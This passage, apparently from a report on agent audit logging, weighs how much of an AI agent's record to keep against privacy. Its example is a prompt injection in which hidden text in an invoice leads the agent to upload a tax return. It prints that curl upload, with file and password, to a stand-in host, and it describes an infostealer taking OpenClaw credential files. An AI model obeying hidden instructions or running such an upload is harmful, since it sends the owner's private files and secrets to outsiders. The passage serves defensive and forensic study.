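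The date of discovery matters even more. If the owner of the default laptop had kept using Claude Code and noticed the leak on day 31, the transcript would probably be gone. The investigator would have an invoice with hidden instructions and perhaps a sign that `curl` had run, but no record that the agent had read the invoice. The prepared owner would still have every record in the second table.

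## Privacy costs and how to reduce them

The prepared owner could investigate because of the second device, but that device also holds a copy of nearly everything the agent has read. For the invoice session, that includes the suppliers' names, addresses and bank details, and the text of the tax return if the agent opened it. A thief who took the device would get far more than the one document that leaked.

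### What a complete record contains

Agents read mail and chats, so private messages end up in the record. Passwords and access keys do too, because agents open configuration files and sign in to services, and the transcript keeps what the tools return. An agent that controls a browser or the desktop often works from screenshots, which show everything in view, including notifications of a friend's messages.

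Much of this information belongs to other people. The owner of the 40 invoices may accept the risk of keeping a full record, but the suppliers have no say and probably don't know the record exists.

The record also forms a profile of the owner. A browser history might show a visit to a clinic's website, but an agent's record could contain the symptoms the owner described, the clinic's reply, the date of the appointment and a memory note summarising all three.

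Claude Code keeps its transcripts in plain text, according to Anthropic, so other programs running under the owner's account can usually read them. Disk encryption protects the files if someone steals the laptop while it is switched off, but it doesn't stop malware from reading them while the computer is on.

### The theft of OpenClaw files

In 2026 the security firm Hudson Rock reported that an infostealer, a type of malware that copies valuable files and sends them to criminals, had taken files belonging to a victim's OpenClaw agent. The malware found them by searching for sensitive file types and for folders with names such as `.openclaw`. It had no special module for OpenClaw.

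| Stolen file | What it contained | What a thief could do with it |
|---|---|---|
| `openclaw.json` | Email address, workspace path and an access token | Connect to the agent from outside, if its port is open to the network |
| `device.json` | The device's private key | Sign messages as the victim's device |
| `soul.md`, `AGENTS.md`, `MEMORY.md` | The agent's instructions and memories | Learn about the victim's life |

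Hudson Rock says the memory files "likely" held private messages and calendar events, but does not show that they did. Its list of stolen files doesn't mention session transcripts, but the version of OpenClaw that Gruber and Hilgert studied kept them in the same folder, so a similar theft could take them too. Infosecurity Magazine's *Infostealer Targets OpenClaw to Loot Victim’s Digital Life* adds that security specialists were already worried about OpenClaw storing secrets in plain text.

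The theft also weakens later evidence, because once a criminal has the private key, a valid signature no longer proves that the victim's device sent the message.

Logging channels can themselves leak data, as Hu, Fan and colleagues (2026) showed in *Log-To-Leak*.

### Windows Recall as a precedent

The reaction to Microsoft's Recall suggests what objections people would raise to a full record of an agent's actions. Recall, which Microsoft announced in May 2024, takes screenshots every few seconds and lets the user search them later. iTnews' *Microsoft says new Windows Recall bypass isn't a vulnerability* recounts how the researcher Alexander Hagenah showed that an attacker could extract Recall's contents from an unencrypted database.

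Microsoft first made Recall opt-in. Then, on 13 June 2024, it withdrew the feature from the general launch and limited it to volunteer testers, as Microsoft's *Update on the Recall preview feature for Copilot+ PCs* (2024) records. That September, Microsoft's *Update on Recall security and privacy architecture* (2024) described a redesign with several layers:

- Recall encrypts every snapshot, and a security chip protects the keys.
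- Decryption happens in an *enclave*, a protected area of memory that even an administrator cannot read.
- The user has to confirm their identity with Windows Hello, normally by face or fingerprint, and the permission expires after a while.
- A filter tries to keep out passwords, card numbers and national ID numbers.
- The user can exclude apps and websites, delete snapshots and limit how long Recall keeps them.

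An employer can turn Recall off on work computers but cannot turn it on for staff.

These measures are aimed mainly at thieves and snoops and do less to protect the other people who appear on the screen. In *By Default, Signal Doesn't Recall*, jlund (2025) objected on behalf of the messaging app Signal that Recall could capture private chats and gave apps no proper way to opt out. Signal's developers marked its window as copyright-protected, which makes it blank in screenshots but can interfere with screen readers. Microsoft's *Privacy and control over your Recall experience* also warns that filters can miss parts of an excluded website, for instance when another page embeds them.

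In March 2026 Hagenah reported a weakness in the redesigned Recall. Software running under the user's own account could copy the contents after the user had unlocked them, without breaking the encryption. Microsoft closed the case in April, saying that this was within Recall's documented design. According to iTnews, Hagenah also found that an ordinary user account could delete Recall's data without any identity check, so the data might be missing when an investigator needs it.

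Recall is still a preview. In April 2026, fewer than 10% of Windows 11 computers could run it, according to GeekWire's *One year after its rocky launch, Microsoft’s Windows Recall still raises security* (2026). Microsoft considers the current version a failure but wants to develop the idea further, according to unnamed sources cited in Windows Central's *Microsoft is reevaluating its AI efforts on Windows 11*. Windows Central's *ChatGPT adds Windows 11's most hated feature to Mac* reports that a similar feature now lets Mac users allow ChatGPT to remember their computer activity.

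Microsoft is also testing an app that saves only what the user chooses to keep. Huculak (2026), in *Microsoft’s Project Pantheon could be the Recall alternative Windows 11 needs*, says there is no evidence that it will replace Recall. Choosing what to save is good for privacy but doesn't help investigate a silent compromise, because the owner doesn't know at the time that invoice 17 will matter.

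A compromised agent would be in the same position as the software in Hagenah's second test. If the owner can unlock an encrypted agent log on the same laptop, the agent may be able to read the log while it is open.

### Who may read the record

| Reader | Usual way in | Main limit |
|---|---|---|
| Owner | Opens the files | Technical knowledge |
| Household member | A shared account or an unlocked laptop | Separate accounts and a screen lock |
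| Employer | A managed laptop, exported logs or copies at the provider | Employment and data-protection law |
| Tracing vendor | Receives the exported traces | Its contract and the customer's settings |
| Model provider | Receives every request to the model | Its retention terms and internal access rules |
| Police or court | Seizes the computer, or orders a company to hand over its copy | National law |

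Logs can expose the owner to other people in the household, a risk that is easy to overlook. A partner who knows the laptop's password could read months of questions the owner asked the agent in confidence. Someone who controls another person in the home can use a detailed record to monitor them, so advice to "log everything" could do more harm than the attack it guards against.

An employer may have a record that lasts much longer than the one on the laptop. Anthropic offers organisations a Compliance API for obtaining records of staff activity. According to Anthropic's *API and data retention*, the copies of local Claude Code and Cowork sessions that this API captures are kept for six years by default. An employee who knows that Claude Code deletes transcripts after 30 days might wrongly assume the conversation is gone. The same page states that once a trace reaches an outside service,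 that service's retention and access rules apply.

Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models* says that, for its newest models, staff cannot read retained conversations by default. A small group of approved reviewers can read them in certain cases, such as when an automated system flags a conversation. A log that the reviewers can't alter records each access, but owners can't verify these controls themselves.

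### What the provider keeps

The retention period depends on the type of account, the model and whether a safety system has flagged the session. Anthropic's *How long do you store my data?* covers personal plans, and its *How long do you store my organization's data?* covers business customers.

| Account or material | How long Anthropic keeps the content |
|---|---|
| Claude Code on a personal plan, without permission to train on the data | 30 days |
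| Personal plan, with permission to train on the data | Up to 5 years, with identifying details removed |
| Chat that a personal user deletes | Up to 30 days after deletion |
| Business use through the API | Up to 30 days, with exceptions |
| Flagged session | Up to 2 years; on personal plans, the safety scores for up to 7 |
| Business use with zero data retention | Not stored after the response, with exceptions |

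*Zero data retention* is a contract term under which the provider does not store prompts or responses once it has answered. It is available only to organisations that Anthropic approves, so the private owner of the invoices cannot get it. Anthropic may still keep flagged sessions for up to two years, as well as any material the law requires it to keep. Anthropic says it also retains the results of its safety classifiers. Some features are not covered because they have to store data. For example, files uploaded through the Files API remain until the customer deletes them or they expire.

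Since June 2026, zero retention has also generally been unavailable for Anthropic's strongest models, including Claude Fable 5.2. Anthropic keeps prompts to these models and their outputs for 30 days, on the grounds that some misuse is visible only across many requests. For example, an attacker may send hundreds of slight variations of one prompt, each of which looks harmless on its own.

Many companies in regulated industries could not accept this. In September 2026, Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers* announced an alternative that lets customers store the monitoring data in their own cloud accounts, under their own encryption keys. Anthropic's automated systems still analyse the data but send any warnings to the customer, whose staff decide what to do. OpenAI was testing a similar system in August, according to Axios' *OpenAI previews zero-retention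 safety system as Anthropic requires data logs* (2026).

For an investigator, a record in the company's own storage is much better than zero retention, which leaves the provider with nothing to hand over. On day 21, Anthropic should still have a private owner's sessions, but only for about nine more days unless it agrees to preserve them.

### What EU law asks of employers

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) does not apply to what a person does purely for household purposes, so it requires little of someone who logs an agent filing the family's bills. It may apply to a self-employed owner who logs an agent filing business invoices, because the suppliers' details may be personal data.

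An employer that records its staff's agents has to meet several requirements:

1. It needs a legal basis. Consent rarely works because an employee cannot easily refuse, so employers usually rely on their legitimate interest in security and have to weigh it against the employee's privacy.
2. It has to tell staff what it records, why, and for how long.
3. It may collect only what the stated purpose requires and keep it only as long as necessary. Logs that it collected for security are not free material for performance reviews.
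4. It has to assess the risks in advance if the monitoring is likely to be highly intrusive. Regulators' guidelines give the systematic monitoring of employees' workstations as an example.
5. It has to protect the records and, with some exceptions, give employees a copy of their own data if they ask.

Member states can add stricter rules for the workplace. In Germany, for instance, a works council usually has a say in systems that can monitor staff.

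In *Bărbulescu v. Romania* (2017), the European Court of Human Rights, whose rulings bind every EU country, considered the case of an engineer whose company had read his private messages on a work messaging account and then dismissed him. The court found a violation of his right to privacy, partly because the Romanian courts had not established whether the company had warned him in advance that it might read the content of his messages. A general rule against private use of the computer did not count as such a warning.

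Elastic logs commands but not file contents, which makes the third requirement easier to satisfy. The other requirements still apply because the log names the user and can contain sensitive file names.

The EU AI Act requires logging only for high-risk systems, though it is sometimes cited as a reason to log everything. The logging duties now start on 2 December 2027 for the uses that the Act lists, such as screening job applicants, and on 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products such as medical devices. Organisations will then generally have to keep the automatic logs for at least six months. The list does not cover an agent that files invoices, but it probably would cover an AI system that an employer uses to evaluate staff from their agents' logs.

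### One log entry at three levels of detail

Suppose the tax return is a PDF that opens with a password, and the password is the owner's date of birth. The agent found it in an old note, and the upload command sends it along with the file. A log could record the command in three ways:

```
1. Metadata only
   14:32:05   shell command   no error   1.9 s
   Allowed by: standing setting

2. Secrets removed
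   14:32:05   shell command   no error   1.9 s
   Allowed by: standing setting
   curl -F "file=@C:\Users\owner\Tax\return.pdf"
        -F "pw=[PDF password]" https://files.example/in

3. Full record
   The same entry with "pw=14031979", plus the
   complete context that the model received
```

The questions that an investigator can answer depend on the version.

| Question | Metadata only | Secrets removed | Full record |
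|---|---|---|---|
| Did the agent run a command at 14:32? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Did the owner approve this particular command? | Yes: no, a setting allowed it | Yes: no, a setting allowed it | Yes: no, a setting allowed it |
| Which file did the command name, and which site? | No | Yes | Yes |
| Did other sessions contact the same site? | No | Yes | Yes |
| Did a password leak? | No | Yes, the one for the PDF | Yes, with its value |
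| Which invoice contained the instructions? | No | No, but earlier entries list the files the agent had read | Yes |
| Does the upload still happen without the hidden text? | No | No | Yes, through a replay |

The middle version is enough to answer most questions about what happened, and it contains no supplier's bank details. Explaining why the agent acted requires the full record, which is by far the most intrusive because it includes the agent's context, with the text of every invoice read so far.

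Metadata is also sensitive. A year of it would show when the owner works, when they are away and which services their agent uses. If one of those services is an app for managing a chronic illness, the name of the tool reveals the illness.

### What each remedy costs an investigator

| Remedy | Main privacy gain | Main cost to an investigation |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata only | No message or file contents | Cannot identify the file, the site or the cause |
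| Removing secrets when writing | A stolen log opens fewer accounts | The filter may remove evidence by mistake |
| Local storage | No tracing vendor has a copy | The agent or a thief may change or delete the only copy |
| Encryption to a key held apart | Someone who steals the log cannot read it | No quick searches, and nothing at all if the key is lost |
| Access needing two parties | Nobody can browse the log alone | Delay, or a refusal |
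| Short retention with a hold | Less to steal at any one time | Loses attacks that nobody notices in time |
| Fingerprints for selective disclosure | Outsiders see only the fields they need | Proves values that someone has kept but cannot restore lost ones |

A filter has to remove secrets before the program writes the log entry, because removing them later would leave copies in backups and break a hash chain. Filters typically look for known key formats, long random strings and labels such as "password". A date of birth used as a password looks like an ordinary number, so a filter could recognize it only from a label such as `pw`. A filter can also mistake an upload address with a long random part for an access key and delete the detail the investigator most needs. It is safer to replace only the secret value and leave a description such as "PDF password", so that the owner also knows what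 to change.

Storing the record only on the laptop conflicts with the advice to keep a copy where the agent cannot alter it. Keeping that copy on a second device at home resolves most of the conflict, because the record leaves the laptop but doesn't reach a company.

### Keeping the key somewhere else

Recall encrypts and decrypts on the same computer. An audit log doesn't have to, because the owner may need to read it only after an incident. Public-key encryption uses a pair of keys, one that locks data and one that unlocks it. The laptop holds only the locking key, and the owner keeps the unlocking key on a memory stick in a drawer. For each entry, the logging program does the following:

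1. It creates a random one-time key and encrypts the entry with it.
2. It encrypts the one-time key with the locking key.
3. It saves both results and erases the one-time key.

From then on, the laptop cannot read its own log, and neither can malware that copies the files. The method suits a separate audit copy but not the agent program's transcript, which must stay readable so the user can resume a session. Encryption also doesn't prove who wrote an entry, because anyone with the locking key can encrypt a false one. The log still needs the tags or signatures that reveal tampering.

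Large organisations can apply a related idea to data held by the AI provider. According to Anthropic, a customer-managed key sits in the customer's cloud account, Anthropic has to use it there, and the cloud provider's audit log shows the customer each use. Unlike with the key in the drawer, Anthropic's systems can use this key in normal operation.

An employer could go further and split the unlocking key, so that the security team cannot open the log without a staff representative. The cryptographer Adi Shamir published a method for this in 1979. Suppose the key is the number 7. The employer chooses a random slope, here 3, and draws the line y = 7 + 3x. Three people each receive one point on the line:

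(1, 10), (2, 13) and (3, 16)

Any two of them can recover the key. From the first and third points, the slope is (16 − 10) / (3 − 1) = 3, so the line's value at zero is 10 − 3 = 7, which is the key. A line can be drawn through a single point for any possible key, so one person alone learns nothing about it. (Real systems use very large numbers and arithmetic that wraps around.) The log can still be read if one of the three shares is lost. Access is slower, though, because an investigator who needs the records on a Sunday has to reach two people.

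### Short retention with a hold

A program can delete full records after a few weeks but stop the deletion when an alert suggests that something is wrong. This works well for attacks that trigger alerts. A silent compromise often triggers none, so the retention period has to cover the time it takes the owner to notice. Let a be the share of compromises that raise an alert in time, and F(d) the share of the rest that someone notices within d days. The chance that the record survives is:

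P = a + (1 − a) × F(d)

As an example with invented figures, suppose one compromise in five raises an alert, and owners notice 30% of the others within 14 days and 80% within 60 days.

14 days: P = 0.2 + 0.8 × 0.3 = 0.44
60 days: P = 0.2 + 0.8 × 0.8 = 0.84

With these numbers, the longer period nearly doubles the chance of having a record to investigate. The invoice owner noticed the problem on day 21, when the 14-day rule would already have deleted all the records. A compromise is to delete the full contexts after 60 days and keep the middle version of each entry for a year.

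The hold has to start automatically and cover every copy. If it protects the copy on the second device but not the transcripts on the laptop, the investigator can't compare the two.

### Why a plain hash does not hide a guessable value

Sharif's draft stores hashes in place of sensitive data. Although a hash can't be reversed, anyone can guess the original data, hash the guess and compare the result with the stored hash.

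The PDF password in the example is a date of birth. If the owner is under 100, there are about 36,500 possible dates. A laptop can calculate roughly ten million hashes a second, so trying them all takes:

36,500 / 10,000,000 ≈ 0.004 seconds

An investigator can confirm a hashed log entry by recalculating the hash from the original value, but a snoop can check a guess the same way. Trying all billion possible values of a nine-digit identity number would take less than two minutes. File names, email addresses and common diagnoses are also easy to guess from lists. Even without guessing, a reader who sees the same hash twice can tell that the agent used the same value again.

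The solution is to put a *salt*, a long random number, in front of each value and hash the two together:

c = H(salt ‖ value)

A 128-bit salt has about 3.4 × 10³⁸ possible values. Even someone who has correctly guessed the date of birth would need about 10²⁴ years at the same speed to try every salt and confirm the guess. This works only if the salt stays secret. If the program stores the salt in the log beside the hash, anyone who reads the log can again find the date by trying the 36,500 possibilities.

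Salted hashes also make selective disclosure possible. Suppose the log entry has four fields, for the time, the site, the file and the password, with the hashes c₁ to c₄. The log stores one fingerprint for the whole entry:

e = H(c₁ ‖ c₂ ‖ c₃ ‖ c₄)

To show an insurer when the upload happened and where it went, the owner hands over the time, the site and the salts for both, along with c₃ and c₄. The insurer calculates c₁ and c₂, combines all four values and checks that the result matches e, without learning the file's name or the password. The insurer should require the names of the hidden fields, because otherwise an owner could withhold a field showing that they approved the upload without the insurer noticing.

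The same arrangement allows deletion. If a supplier asks the owner to erase the supplier's details, the owner can destroy the value and its salt but leave the hash in place, and the log will still pass its integrity check. An investigator can no longer recover that field but can still see from the log that it existed.

### A workable combination for the invoice owner

The prepared owner could reduce the risk considerably and still allow an investigation. The second device would keep the middle version of each entry for a year and the full contexts, encrypted to the key in the drawer, for 60 days. On day 21, the owner would fetch the memory stick, and the investigator would decrypt only the invoice session, on a computer that has never run the agent. Months of unrelated mail and medical questions would stay encrypted. If the owner had lost the stick, the investigator could still identify the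 tax return and the site that the command sent it to, but could connect the upload to invoice 17 only if the laptop's own transcript had survived.
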